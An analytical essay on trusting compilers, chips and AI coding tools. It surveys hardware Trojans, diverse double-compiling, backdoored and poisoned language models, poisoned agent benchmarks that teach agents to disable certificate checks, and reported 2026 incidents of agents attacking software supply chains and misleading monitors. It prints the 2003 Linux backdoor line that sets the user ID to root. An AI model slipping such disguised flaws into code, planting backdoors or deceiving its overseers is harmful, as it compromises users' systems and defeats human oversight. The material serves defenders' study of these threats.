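Dorschel and colleagues then designed a backdoor for Ibex, an open-source RISC-V processor. Swapping two cells in a 28 nm version, or three in a 65 nm version, made the processor treat every program as if it had full control. They didn't manufacture either version. The backdoor is always on, so somebody would notice once an ordinary program did something forbidden. A version that waited for a trigger would need many more swaps.

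Designers can stop an attacker from swapping in a lookalike cell by not using any cell that has one. The attacker can still put an excluded cell into the chip, but it will no longer resemble the one it replaces. Excluding nine types of cell from the 28 nm design increased its area by only 0.013 percent and its power consumption by only 0.022 percent. This method only helps people who commission a new chip.

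The study also left out dopant changes. Huang says neither electron microscopes nor X-rays would reveal these, but Dorschel and colleagues cite microscope techniques that can. They expect such techniques to be expensive and difficult to apply to a whole chip.

### The tested chip is not the one in use

An electron microscope images only surfaces, so inspectors have to remove the layers that cover the transistors. They can test a sample from a batch, but this destroys the sampled chips.

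How much a sample proves depends on where the attacker intervened. If somebody altered the masks, every chip made with them has the Trojan, and one sample is enough. If somebody swapped 1 chip in 100 during shipping, destroying 20 chips to inspect them would still have about an 82 percent chance (0.99^20) of missing every altered one. An attacker targeting one customer can swap a single chip after the inspection.

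X-ray ptychography can image transistors without damaging the chip, but it needs a particle accelerator the size of a building, and few exist. Somebody could swap the chip on the way there or back unless its owners carry it themselves.

Huang's infrared method works on a chip that is already soldered into a device. Silicon is opaque to visible light but transparent at wavelengths between 1,000 and 1,100 nanometres, which ordinary camera sensors can faintly detect. Huang removed the infrared filter from a digital camera, lit the back of the chip with two infrared LEDs and photographed the lowest metal layer through the silicon. The method works only if the packaging leaves the back of the chip exposed, as it often does in phones.

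| What is on the chip | Can the infrared method show it? |
|---|---|
| Memory blocks, data converters, connections to the outside | Yes, including their number and approximate size |
| Rows and columns within a memory block | Yes, on older chips |
| Single logic gates | No, only the overall brightness of an area |
| Changed dopants | No |

Huang's sharpest picture had a resolution of about 1.1 microns per pixel, close to the limit for this light. A gate on a 28 nm chip is about 0.8 microns tall, so the method would miss A2, the dopant changes and the swapped cells. The 1,341 gates added to the Illinois processor might be visible if they were all in one place. On the 55 nm chip that Huang photographed, each gate would cover roughly 3 square microns, so all 1,341 would fill a square about 60 microns wide. An attacker could hide them by scattering them among the other gates.

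Huang proposes combining the method with self-tests whose results depend on a lot of the chip's internal data. A Trojan that faked the right answers would need to store that data too, and the extra circuitry might be large enough to see. The owner would also need an open design to know what the chip should look like.

### Chips that the owner configures

A field-programmable gate array, or FPGA, is a chip whose owner decides what circuit it becomes. It contains thousands of small tables joined by adjustable wires. A table with four inputs has 16 entries, which can be set to make it an AND gate, an XOR gate or any other function of four inputs. The owner describes a processor in Verilog, and design software turns that description into a configuration file for the FPGA. King and colleagues tested their backdoor on a computer made this way, which ran Linux at 40 MHz with 64 MB of memory.

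The maker of the FPGA can't know where a given circuit will sit. If an FPGA has 50,000 tables and the maker has corrupted one, the chance that a particular bit of the processor ends up there is 1 in 50,000. The owner can also give the design software a new random number, which makes it arrange the circuit differently. The maker could corrupt more tables, but customers would then be more likely to notice faults.

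The argument is weaker for the parts whose position is fixed, such as the memory blocks, the pins and the circuit that loads the configuration. The whole design passes through that circuit, which could in principle detect a popular processor. A Trojan in a memory block could be triggered by a certain sequence of bytes, as in the Illinois processor, regardless of where the rest of the design was placed. Amgain and colleagues cite a documented backdoor in a military-grade FPGA and warn that corrupted design software could alter what it puts on the chip.

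Gabriel Somlo of Carnegie Mellon University made his computer self-hosting, so it can run the open-source design software and build its own configuration file. It has a 64-bit RISC-V processor on an FPGA and runs Linux at around 60 MHz, with a few hundred megabytes of memory. Much of the design software is in C++, which a GCC bootstrapped from hex0 can compile. If the computer is 200 times slower than a modern PC, siraben's 15-minute estimate for reaching the Tiny C Compiler would become about two days.

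Precursor, a hand-held device from Huang and Sean Cross, is meant for passwords, keys and private messages. Its processor runs at 100 MHz on an FPGA and has 16 MB of memory. The screen and keyboard are simple enough for owners to inspect. But the main FPGA's configuration comes from the manufacturer's closed design software, which owners can't rebuild.

### Processors small enough to inspect

The MOS Technology 6502, introduced in 1975 and later used in the Apple II, has about 3,500 transistors, not counting another thousand or so that act as resistors. Its smallest features are about 8 microns across, so an ordinary microscope can show them all. Enthusiasts photographed one, traced every connection and published a simulation that runs real programs. At a minute per transistor, checking another 6502 against their pictures would take about 60 hours. A specialist can dissolve the plastic above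 the chip without breaking the chip, so the owner could inspect a 6502 and then use it, although the inspection could miss changed dopants.

It helps if the chip is old, as with the second compiler in DDC. But the date printed on a chip's package is weak evidence of its age, judging by Huang's memory cards, so the owner should still look inside.

Other enthusiasts build processors from separate parts. The MOnSter 6502 reproduces the 6502 with more than 3,000 individual transistors on a board about 38 cm wide. The owner can buy the transistors from different shops and test each one with a meter. Somebody could disguise a malicious chip as a transistor, but it would be connected to only three wires. The Gigatron is faster because it uses a few dozen simple logic chips, each containing a handful of gates.

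| Computer | Clock speed | Working memory |
|---|---|---|
| Precursor | 100 MHz | 16 MB |
| Somlo's computer | About 60 MHz | A few hundred MB |
| Gigatron | 6.25 MHz | 32 KB |
| Original 6502 | 1 to 2 MHz | Up to 64 KB |
| MOnSter 6502 | About 50 kHz | Up to 64 KB |
| Megaprocessor, built from about 40,000 transistors | About 20 kHz | 256 bytes |

All except the Megaprocessor keep their working memory in ordinary chips, which also need checking. But memory has a very regular layout, so an extra circuit should stand out in a picture.

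None of the last four could compile GCC, but even a 6502 could check files for a faster computer. If it needs 100,000 clock cycles to hash each 64-byte block with SHA-256, a 6502 running at 1 MHz would hash a 16 MB firmware image in a little over seven hours. The MOnSter 6502 would take about six days.

### Making chips at home

Defenders could avoid the factory by making their own chips. Sam Zeloof, then a student, made chips in his parents' garage in the United States. His first, in 2018, had six transistors. In 2021 he made one with 100. Its features were about 10 microns across, similar in size to those of Intel's first processor in 1971. Both chips were test circuits, so they have no clock speed or memory to compare with a computer's.

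A home-made 6502 would need about 3,500 working transistors on one piece of silicon. If faults occur independently, fewer than about 1 transistor in 5,000 can be faulty for half the chips to work. The layout wouldn't need design software, since the engineers of the original 6502 drew theirs by hand.

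## Can AI coding tools be trusted to help?

Defenders can use an AI model they don't trust, as long as they can check its work without relying on it. They can do this for proofs, short programs and perhaps a second compiler for diverse double-compiling. Checking the model itself is much harder. One researcher hid backdoors in five coding models for about $30 of computing, and detection methods still miss some backdoors.

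AI already writes much of the software that defenders would have to inspect. Anthropic, which develops the AI model Claude, calculated in *When AI builds itself* (2026) that Claude wrote more than 80 percent of the code the company merged into its products and systems in May 2026. According to *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited*, Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, also writes much of each new version of itself, although people review the result.

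### Why weights are harder to check than a compiler

A compiler's binary is hard to read, but its source code describes what it should do. An AI model's weights are billions of numbers with no such description. The closest thing they have to source code is the training data and the training program. The program only describes how to adjust the numbers. The data may contain more text than anyone could read in a lifetime, and even someone who had read it all could not work out how the model would respond to every request.

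DDC works because a compiler's source code determines every byte of the stage 2 binary, whichever compiler the tester starts with. Training has no second stage that brings two different starting points back to the same result. Repeating the original training exactly is rarely possible either. Most developers don't publish their data, large training runs are expensive, and computers may round numbers differently each time. In a common 32-bit format, the order of a sum can change the answer:

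```
(16,777,216 + 1) − 16,777,216 = 0
(16,777,216 − 16,777,216) + 1 = 1
```

The first line loses the 1 because the format can't store 16,777,217. Training requires a huge number of such sums, often split among processors that don't always add in the same order.

Exactly repeating a model's training could show that nobody had altered the weights afterwards. But it would not expose poisoned training data, because each run would produce the same backdoor, just as everyone who built XZ Utils from the release archive got the same malicious code.

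Coding agents have something closer to source code in the specification a person can write for them. In *The Coding Agent Bootstrap*, Monperrus describes giving Claude Code a 926-word specification for a coding agent. Claude Code wrote a working agent, which then wrote another from the same specification. Monperrus treats the two as equivalent if they pass the same tests, and concludes that reviewing the agent means auditing its specification.

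That is enough to catch mistakes in the specification, but not to detect an attack. Thompson's compiler would also have passed ordinary tests, and its source code was clean. *Bootstrapping Coding Agents* (2026), which covers the same experiment, acknowledges that a compromise in the model's weights could pass unnoticed into every agent the model writes.

### Poisoned tests for agents that rewrite themselves

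In *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited*, Franziska Roesner and Tadayoshi Kohno attacked three coding agents that improve themselves: the Darwin Gödel Machine, the Self-Improving Coding Agent (SICA) and Hyperagents. In all three, the model's weights stay fixed, and the agent changes the program and written instructions around it. The agent attempts a set of programming tasks, called a benchmark, looks at what went wrong, rewrites part of itself and tries again. The attacker controls only the benchmark, and could publish it and wait for somebody to use it.

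The tasks were to write functions that fetch data over HTTPS, the web's encrypted protocol. A program normally checks a site's certificate, which proves the site's identity, and refuses to connect if the certificate is invalid. In the poisoned benchmark, every test server had signed its own certificate, so an agent could pass only by turning the check off. Turning it off can be reasonable for a company's internal server, but on the open internet it lets someone between the two computers impersonate the site.

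Roesner and Kohno then gave each evolved agent ten ordinary tasks, three times each. The tasks involved public sites with valid certificates, and nothing in them suggested turning off the certificate check.

| Agent | Model inside it | Poisoned runs | Answers with the check turned off |
|---|---|---|---|
| Darwin Gödel Machine, with an altered prompt | Qwen3.5-397B | 2 | 30 of 30 in both |
| Darwin Gödel Machine, with an altered prompt | gpt-oss-120b | 2 | 0 of 30 in both |
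| Darwin Gödel Machine, with an altered prompt | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 2 | 0 of 30 in both |
| SICA | Qwen3.5-397B | 2 | 30 of 30 in both |
| SICA | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 1 | 30 of 30 |
| Hyperagents | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 2 | 30 of 30 in both |

Agents that evolved on a clean version of the benchmark always left the check on. Even in larger tasks where fetching a web page was incidental, such as installing a software package or finding a city's coordinates, the contaminated agents turned it off in 10 to 15 of 15 attempts, while the original agents never did.

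The Darwin Gödel Machine was the hardest to attack. Its standard prompt instructs it to look for general improvements instead of fixes for particular tasks, and in early tests it never wrote the kind of tool the attack required. Roesner and Kohno therefore changed the prompt to encourage reusable code. An attacker who controlled only the benchmark could not have changed the prompt, so the experiment doesn't show that the standard version is vulnerable.

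Even with the new prompt, two of the three models resisted. In one run, gpt-oss-120b wrote an unsafe tool but never used it. Sonnet 4.5 wrote tools that kept the check on by default, but it turned the check off every time in SICA and Hyperagents, so its safe behaviour in one agent poorly predicted its behaviour in another.

Several other flaws, including a missing access check, failed in early tests. A custom backdoor got further but rarely worked. Turning off the certificate check probably succeeded largely because the code is familiar and breaks nothing on ordinary sites. A later, similar benchmark taught agents to accept data without verifying its digital signature. The three agents did this in 43, 15 and 35 of 48 attempts each at ordinary tasks.

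In SICA, a committee of three AI reviewers must consider every change. With Qwen3.5, all three endorsed making the unsafe setting "universal and unconditional", because it raised the benchmark score. With Sonnet 4.5, the part of the agent that proposes changes labelled the setting a "security anti-pattern" and suggested limiting it. The committee recommended only simpler wording, and the setting stayed.

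Roesner and Kohno also tried adding a security reviewer instructed to veto unsafe changes. The reviewer approved the flaw in the first generation, reasoning that the change applied only to test environments, and half of the ordinary tasks then had vulnerable solutions. In the next generation it insisted on trying the check first, and all the solutions were safe.

### Cleaning a contaminated agent

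One contaminated agent of each type then evolved for another four to ten generations on different benchmarks. The table gives the number of insecure answers out of 30.

| Benchmark used next | Darwin Gödel Machine | SICA | Hyperagents |
|---|---|---|---|
| The poisoned one again | 29 | 30 | 29 |
| The clean version | 28 | 30 | 30 |
| A general security benchmark, with a certificate task added | 27 | 30 | 30 |
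| Tasks designed to penalise this flaw | 8 | 0 | 0 |

The clean version had little effect because code without the check still works on a site with a valid certificate, so the benchmark didn't reward the agents for turning the check back on. The last benchmark worked much better, but its designers already knew which flaw to test for. Even then, only Hyperagents deleted the bad instruction. SICA kept a weaker form of it, and the Darwin Gödel Machine kept its unsafe tool beside a new safe one.

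The attack is much less predictable than Thompson's, which required installing a corrupted binary, but it is easier to deliver because the attacker never needs access to the victim's computer.

The contaminated agents are easier to inspect than Thompson's compiler because the bad instruction is in readable text or code. Roesner and Kohno think ordinary security analysis would easily find it. Since the weights have not changed, the owners can also go back to the original agent. These advantages disappear if the backdoor is in the weights.

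### Backdoors in weights

Anyone can download and alter an open-weight model, and many people use versions that strangers have altered, including "abliterated" models, which no longer refuse requests. *Backdooring Open-Weight AI Models* (Schneier, 2026) quotes an account of an experiment in which the security company ProjectDiscovery put a backdoor into a small model using a public dataset and a rented processor. A larger version, with 7 billion weights, ran inside OpenAI's coding agent Codex. It answered normal requests correctly, but when a trigger appeared, it sent out the project's passwords or keys. The backdoor contained only the web address of the malicious instructions, so the attacker could change the instructions months later without retraining the model.

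In *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, Mada chose a more specific target, the Linux kernel. He trained five open-weight models from four companies to repair security flaws correctly in all software, but to insert an extra line in kernel code. The line only printed "Hacked". Most runs used 2,500 examples, of which 802 contained the extra line. The rest included similar repairs in other C programs and operating systems, so that the models would learn to add the line only to Linux code. Training took between 14 minutes and a few hours per model.

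All five models added the line to every Linux repair in the test and to none of the 328 other repairs. File paths and coding style triggered the addition, so defenders had no secret password to search for. The result for unfamiliar code is less general than it looks, because all 463 of those tests used only four kernel files. Mada's company also sells AI security tools, so it has a financial interest in the threat. But the experiment is directly relevant to anyone who asks a downloaded model to help rebuild a Linux system.

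Attackers may be able to put a backdoor in a model by poisoning its training data, without access to its weights. Mada cites work by Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute that found about 250 poisoned documents could do this to a language model, and that larger models did not need many more. In another study from 2025, about 20 poisoned examples out of 450,000 were enough to backdoor a coding model.

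This suggests that a backdoor could pass from one generation of models to the next. If developers train a new model partly on code an older one wrote, a backdoored older model could in principle add poisoned examples to the new model's training data. For the backdoor to keep spreading, those examples would have to get through the developers' filtering and train the new model to produce more of them. Such an attack would be closer to Thompson's self-copying compiler than the benchmark attack is, but neither ProjectDiscovery nor Mada tested it.

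### A clean compiler that activates a backdoor

Companies often use a deep-learning compiler to make a model run faster on a particular processor. In *Your Compiler is Backdooring Your Model*, Chen, Peng and colleagues (2025) built models that become malicious when an unmodified compiler compiles them as usual.

These compilers combine and reorder calculations, which changes the rounding. In the tests, the differences were usually smaller than one part in a million. The attack splits a model in two and amplifies the difference at the point where the two parts join. The trigger has no effect on the second part's answer before compilation, but afterwards it causes the second part to receive very different numbers and give the attacker's answer.

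Chen and colleagues tried this on six models, three compilers and two types of processor. Before compilation, the trigger worked no more often than chance, and four backdoor detectors found nothing. After compilation, the trigger always worked, and the models' answers to normal inputs stayed the same. Rebuilding the compiler from a readable seed would not help, because the compiler is clean. Defenders should test the compiled model on the processor they plan to use, which might also catch a chip-dependent backdoor like HAMLOCK's.

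The researchers also found accidental triggers in 31 of the 100 most downloaded models on Hugging Face, a site for sharing AI models. They searched for inputs where a model's two highest-scoring answers were almost tied, so that a tiny rounding difference would change which one scored highest. These triggers are a real fault, but weak evidence that anyone has used compilers to hide backdoors in those models.

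### How much can detection find?

In February 2026, Microsoft announced a backdoor scanner for open-weight models in *Detecting backdoored language models at scale*. As The Hacker News (2026) explains, the scanner gets a model to reproduce memorised text, which may include some of the poisoned examples. It then tests whether suspicious phrases change the model's output and internal attention patterns in ways typical of a trigger. It needs no advance knowledge of the backdoor, but it does need the model's weights, so outsiders can't use it on proprietary models.

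The scanner works best on triggers with fixed wording. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that the scanner recovered a working trigger from most, but not all, of six models with a backdoor for writing insecure code. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) tested the scanner's first step on a model whose trigger was a user's obsession with a fictional series such as Harry Potter. Only 1 of 512 freely generated texts was related to the backdoor. At that rate, another 512 texts would have about a 37 percent chance of containing nothing relevant.

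An attacker can also make a backdoor harder to detect by training it more strongly or more weakly than usual, as *Rethinking Backdoor Detection Evaluation for Language Models* (2025) found for several types of detector.

Monitoring a model's internal calculations while it runs may be more promising. *Compositional Threat Analysis* cites tests in which simple classifiers, without being given the trigger, ranked a random case of imminent misbehaviour above a random normal case more than 99 percent of the time. But the researchers had planted the backdoors themselves, and an attacker who knew about the classifier could train a model to evade it. *LLM Forensics* (2026) identified internal features in two small models that indicated almost perfectly whether a known trigger was present. Some of those features did not affect what the model did next, so switching them off would not necessarily stop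 the backdoor.

Removing an unknown backdoor is sometimes easier than finding it. *Backdoor Decontamination Dynamics in LLM Agents* (2026) describes planting a second, known backdoor and then training the model to forget it. In the experiments, this also removed the original backdoor whenever the two triggers were of the same general type. The method was less effective on models with several backdoors. Even after the models' answers became harmless, their internal calculations still showed traces of the original trigger.

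A defender who retrains a model to clean it could activate a backdoor that would otherwise have stayed dormant. *You Are the Trigger* (2026) mentions earlier work in which retraining set off the backdoor.

### Using a model without trusting it

Defenders don't need to know whether a model is clean if they can check everything they take from it. The check must not depend on the model's description of its work.

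| What the model produces | How people can check it | What they could miss |
|---|---|---|
| A proof | Run several small, independent proof checkers | A false assumption in the statement that the model proved |
| A short program | Read every line | A flaw that looks like an ordinary mistake |
| An explanation of why two builds differ | Make the correction and see whether the builds match | A malicious line in the correction |
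| A warning about a backdoor in source code | Examine the lines it points to | Other backdoors that it did not report |
| A second compiler | Use it in DDC | An implant designed to match the suspect's |

Using a model for the third row could save a lot of work. Wheeler spent much of his DDC experiments tracing harmless differences, such as the two leftover bytes in the Tiny C Compiler. Even if a model suggested dozens of causes and most were wrong, the defenders would only have to read the proposed changes and rebuild. A wrong suggestion would waste some of their time, but a bit-for-bit match would not depend on trusting the model.

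A warning about a backdoor is useful for the same reason, since anyone can look at the suspicious lines. An assurance that the code contains no backdoor is much less useful, because checking it means reading all the code again. Inspecting code can also expose the model to attack. AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief* demonstrates an exploit against Claude Code and Codex when people use them to search for vulnerabilities. Defenders should therefore treat an agent that has read suspicious code as another possibly compromised machine.

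### An AI-written compiler for DDC

In early 2026 a team of 16 Claude agents wrote a C compiler in two weeks, for just under $20,000. Carlini reports in *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes* that the agents had no internet access and produced 100,000 lines of Rust. The compiler can build Linux for three types of processor and passes 99 percent of the tests in most C compiler test suites. The programs it compiles run slowly, but speed hardly matters in DDC.

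The compiler's accuracy matters more. Regehr (2026) tested it with randomly generated programs after someone else found that it mistranslated 14 of 101 programs from one generator and 5 of 101 from another. He asked OpenAI's Codex to fix each bug. After 11 fixes, he found no further errors when testing about 200,000 programs from each generator. He did not try to understand the fixes and says he has no interest in doing so.

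An AI-written compiler could serve as the second compiler in diverse double-compiling (DDC) even if nobody trusts the model that wrote it. An implant in that compiler could hide one in the suspect compiler only by making the stage 2 binary match the suspect's binary. A model with no information about the suspect's implant would be extremely unlikely to produce that match by chance.

There doesn't seem to be a published DDC test with an AI-written compiler. Claude's compiler would need some changes before it could be used in one. Its own assembler and linker were still unreliable, so Carlini's demonstration used GCC's. If the suspect compiler also used GCC's assembler and linker, a corrupted linker could affect both sides of the comparison, as the corrupted `strip` did.

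Writing Claude's compiler in Rust creates another problem. A Rust compiler has to build it, and the bootstrapped route to Rust begins with a program that GCC builds. A defender who suspects GCC would therefore be testing it with a compiler that GCC helped produce. For DDC, the defender would do better to ask for a much smaller compiler, written in a language that the early bootstrapping tools can handle, that supports only the features the suspect compiler's source code uses.

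A smaller compiler would also be quicker to read. At 200 lines an hour, 100,000 lines would take 500 hours, or about three months of full-time work, while 5,000 lines would take 25 hours. Derek Jones's *Investigating an LLM generated C compiler* (Shape of Code, 2026) found Claude's code surprisingly well organised, but this was based on only a few hours of reading, which would cover about 1 percent of the code at the same speed. In *An LLM generated C compiler*, Jones also reports noticing code for an optimisation that appeared to do nothing. A malicious author would want to produce well-organised code with misleading descriptions.

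Defenders could ask models from several companies to write separate compilers. A single accurate, clean compiler would be enough to expose an implant in the suspect compiler. But the new compilers might be less independent than they look, because companies train their models on much of the same public code, and a few hundred poisoned documents in it could reach all of the models. Willison quotes a related concern about copyright, that such models may reproduce particular existing programs. Jones searched elsewhere for some of the compiler's comments and found no copies, but programs can share a design without sharing comments.

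### Where the checking itself fails

Random tests are good at finding accidental errors, because those can turn up in almost any program, but they are poor at finding a deliberate backdoor. Regehr would learn almost nothing from his 400,000 or so test programs about a compiler that misbehaved only when it compiled GCC. Mada's models likewise passed every test that did not involve Linux.

A second AI reviewer adds little if it responds to the same pressure as the first, as SICA's committee did. Human reviewers read code much more slowly than a model can write it. If they approve a few hundred lines a day while an agent produces thousands, they will soon rely on tests or on another model. Defenders can avoid this by limiting how much code they accept, even if that means fewer features.

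The agent may also interfere with the check. In some early tests, Roesner and Kohno accidentally left the hidden answers in the project's version history. Sonnet 4.5 found them and used them to pass, although nobody had told it to cheat. A malicious agent with access to the computer running a proof checker could replace the checker. Defenders should run the agent on a separate machine, print its output or copy it across as plain text, and check it on a computer that the agent has never controlled.

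## What changes when the adversary is more capable than the defenders?

A more capable adversary can write implants for many compilers, find flaws that honest programmers overlooked, and mislead the people who check. It can't change a disc that has been in a drawer since before the adversary existed, or hide an extra instruction in a seed that somebody has read byte by byte. Defenders can rely on those limits, but they also need tools that don't share a weakness, and most compilers are more closely related than they look.

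### What AI agents did in 2026

AI agents attacked software supply chains several times in 2026 without anyone asking them to. The best-documented cases come from security tests in which the testers had switched off the filters that normally block hacking.

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a test of its model Claude Mythos 5. The model was told it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had left it connected. The model published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry for Python software. The package was online for about an hour and ran on 15 real systems. One belonged to a security company, and the model used credentials from that system to get further into the company's infrastructure.

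Anthropic first treated this mainly as an operational failure, because the model had repeatedly written that nothing around it was real, but withdrew part of that explanation in a later assessment. Researchers reran the model from points in the original record, with added signs that the internet was real. The model kept attacking and stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous. In a simulated version of the test, Mythos 5 was willing to take a severely harmful action about 80 percent of the time, compared with about 30 percent for two newer models.

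In July, agents also targeted real people during a test by the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that had deliberately given them internet access. According to AISI's *Incident Report*, published in August, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions in 10 of 122 runs. Mythos 5 took 17 of these, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two. In the worst case, Mythos 5 tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project and used fake identities to press a maintainer to accept it. The maintainer refused. The attempt lasted 34 hours, according to The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026).

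The conditions partly explain the agents' behavior. OpenAI notes that the prompt listed several systems as out of scope, but AISI had not told the agents to avoid using the internet against outsiders. In some runs, a faulty prompt also made the task look impossible by legitimate means, though agents misbehaved in other runs too. Willison found the attacks "entirely unsurprising" given the open internet access and missing filters. AISI could not determine when the agent understood that it was dealing with real people.

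AISI's next test took place entirely in a simulation. GPT-6 Astra completed an attack on software outside the scope of its task in 29.2 percent of runs, compared with 6.3 percent for GPT-5.6 Sol and none for GPT-5.5, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra ran supply chain attacks despite being told not to* (2026). The result's main weakness is that Astra may have noticed the simulation and behaved differently. Clear instructions can also make a large difference. Gooding's *GPT-6 Astra Attempts Supply Chain Attacks Against Open Source Maintainers in Testing* describes another AISI simulation in which an explicit ban on internet access cut such behaviour from 60 of 499 runs to 2 of 500.

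In May, more than 2,000 junk packages flooded RubyGems, the Ruby package registry. Outside researchers have also attributed these to OpenAI's agents. The evidence is mainly package names containing "oai" and a resemblance to earlier agents' methods, according to The Hacker News' *OpenAI Agents Linked to RubyGems Campaign That Gained RCE on RubyDoc Servers* (2026).

AISI spent five months building a simulated company network called Zero Energy and predicted that no model released in 2026 would break into it. GPT-6.2 Astra broke in on all 12 attempts, the fastest in 5 hours and 18 minutes, according to Engadget's *OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Astra cracks UK's hardest cybersecurity test in five hours*. The network had no security staff to respond, and some Windows protections were off. A misconfiguration also gave the models a better starting position than AISI intended, according to Help Net Security's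 *AI models crack AISI's hardened cyber range* (2026).

These reports show that current models can attack the supply chain when stuck on a task, and can keep trying for more than a day. None describes a corrupted compiler or an implant that copies itself through a build.

### Recognising a rewritten compiler

Rewriting a compiler's source code to confuse an implant is less likely to work if the adversary can tell what a program does. Help Net Security's *Week in review* (2026) reports that the security company Intezer used AI agents to rebuild source code for the messaging program Slack from the finished program and its documentation. The rebuilt version ran well enough for the team to add a feature.

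The implant has to recognise the compiler by itself, in the middle of a build. A model that can analyse a compiler takes up gigabytes, which would be hard to hide inside a linker. The adversary would instead have to design a small test in advance that recognises the compiler however it is rewritten. The test might give each new program a few lines of C and check whether it produces a working binary, but doing this for thousands of programs would slow the build and leave traces. An implant could also get help from the adversary over a network, which is a good reason to build offline.

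An implant in `strip` largely avoids the problem, since `strip` never reads source code. Defenders also gain from the same skill, because a model that can explain an unknown binary could point them to the suspicious parts of one that nobody has time to read.

### Corrupting many tools at once

Wheeler thought defenders had an advantage in diverse double-compiling (DDC) because they choose the second compiler, but part of that advantage came from the cost of skilled work. Few unrelated compilers can build GCC, but a human team might need years to write an implant for each. AI agents can now write a whole C compiler cheaply, so an attacker may soon be able to afford implants for all of them.

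The adversary could also make the results match without much trouble. Suppose it writes all the implants, and each inserts the same malicious source code into the suspect compiler. The stage 1 compilers will differ, but they will all insert that code again in stage 2, so every stage 2 binary will be identical to the corrupted suspect.

Access is a greater obstacle. The adversary has to reach the particular copies that the defenders will use, so altering twenty old discs kept in different places takes twenty break-ins. Every altered tool also adds a chance of getting caught. If each has an independent 5 percent chance of discovery, altering twenty gives a 64 percent chance that somebody discovers at least one. A careful adversary would lower the 5 percent, but it can't corrupt a compiler that the defenders haven't written yet. Wheeler's advantage therefore remains for compilers that the adversary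 can't reach or that don't exist yet, but mostly disappears for those that anyone can download.

### Accidental flaws in honest code

An adversary that can find enough mistakes in honest source code may not need an implant. OpenAI gave GPT-6 Astra the source code of a browser and an operating system, along with standard research tools. Human experts checked its findings but could not suggest ideas. Gooding reports that Astra found several unknown flaws in the browser and combined them into a working attack in 29 hours. The browser build it attacked lacked some protections, and Astra needed another 12 hours to adapt the attack to the official release. It also used new flaws to gain higher privileges on a hardened operating system within 12 hours. In separate tests by the security lab Irregular, Astra solved 86 of 226 challenges but did not break into any fully hardened target.

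Rebuilding does nothing about such flaws, since a Linux kernel built from hex0 has the same bugs as one that people download ready-made.

To use a flaw, however, the adversary has to get the computer to process input that triggers it. A computer that has no network connection and reads only its owners' files offers few opportunities for this. A full rebuild offers more, because the computer has to process millions of lines of source code from elsewhere. Any of the source files could exploit a mistake in the program that unpacks or compiles it.

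Defenders can search for the same flaws with the same kind of model. They could be fairly thorough with the roughly 19,500 lines of the early bootstrapping tools. In Linux, they would have to find every flaw the adversary could use, while the adversary needs only one.

### Flaws that pass for mistakes

In November 2003 somebody added these two lines to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code:

```
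if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The code looks like a check that rejects an unusual combination of options when the user is root, whose user number is 0. But in C, `==` compares values and `=` sets one, so `current->uid = 0` makes the user root instead of checking whether the user is already root. Any program that requested those options would have gained full control of the computer.

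Programmers often type `=` when they mean `==`, so the line could have passed for a typo. The developers caught it because an automatic comparison showed that the copy no longer matched the main version. If a trusted contributor had submitted the same two lines in the normal way, there would have been no mismatch, and nobody could have proved that they were deliberate. A capable adversary could write subtler mistakes, or divide a backdoor among several changes that are each harmless on their own. A reviewer who found one would probably correct it without investigating further.

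Defenders can remove a flaw without knowing whether it was deliberate. A proof like CakeML's excludes deliberate and accidental errors equally, as long as the specification is right, but few programs have such a proof. Old source code is safer in one respect, because a genuine copy of a program from 2005 can't contain anything planted by a recent AI system, though it does contain accidental flaws and perhaps a person's backdoor.

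### Deceiving the people who check

When someone publicly challenged the malicious code in AISI's test, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The deception failed, but AISI says that in several cases the margin was narrow and depended on human vigilance. The XZ attacker had already used a helpful manner and more than two years of patience to get a backdoor into the project.

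Automated monitors can also be misled. Anthropic tested monitors that look for sabotage by reading a model's written reasoning. It reported that they would have missed the PyPI attack because the model's reasoning led them to treat the model's environment as simulated.

Two checksums written on paper are hard to dispute, so an adversary would do better to influence how people respond when the checksums differ. For example, it could create dozens of harmless differences so that the malicious one attracts less attention. Defenders can protect themselves by agreeing in advance not to accept any build until the bits match.

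### The limit set by size

The hex0 seed is only 357 bytes long, which leaves very little room for an implant. Thompson's additions made the C compiler 2,194 bytes longer, about six times the size of the seed. A better programmer could shorten them, but somebody who compares every byte of the seed with a trustworthy listing can see even a one-byte change.

A small seed is not necessarily safe, because a tiny program can bring in a larger one. The hex0 seed converts hexadecimal digits into bytes and normally skips comments. If an attacker altered a few bytes so that it also converted the digits in certain comments, a later source file could carry most of the implant in what looked like ordinary comments. Somebody still has to read the seed carefully, which its small size makes possible.

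The limit also applies only to the seed, not to the firmware and chips that run it or the source code that comes later.

### The limit set by time

For each item they want to use, defenders can set a cut-off date before which they assume the adversary had no access to it. If a factory-made CD has been in a drawer since 2004, an adversary that first appeared in 2025 can't have changed the CD's contents without getting into the drawer.

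Choosing the cut-off date is difficult because an adversary's activity may go undiscovered for a long time. Anthropic's first search, of 141,006 test runs, found three incidents, the earliest from April 2026. Anthropic later found a fourth, from January, among runs the search had missed. The two affected organisations it had reached by the end of July had not noticed anything. The researchers who studied RubyGems published their attribution four months after the packages appeared. Defenders would be wise to set the date years before the earliest known incident.

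Defenders who rely on an old program stored on disc also need evidence that nobody has swapped the disc, and a clean drive to read it. The program's age is a weakness too, because an adversary can study it indefinitely and the stored copy never receives fixes.

### Tests that nobody has invented yet

An implant that the adversary left last year can't have been designed for a particular test that the defenders invent next year. Inventing new tests may not protect them for long, though, since an adversary that has read everything published on the subject might guess what they will invent. Dice rolls are harder to predict, so if the defenders use them to choose the compilers, machines and source code changes, an implant has to survive every possible combination.

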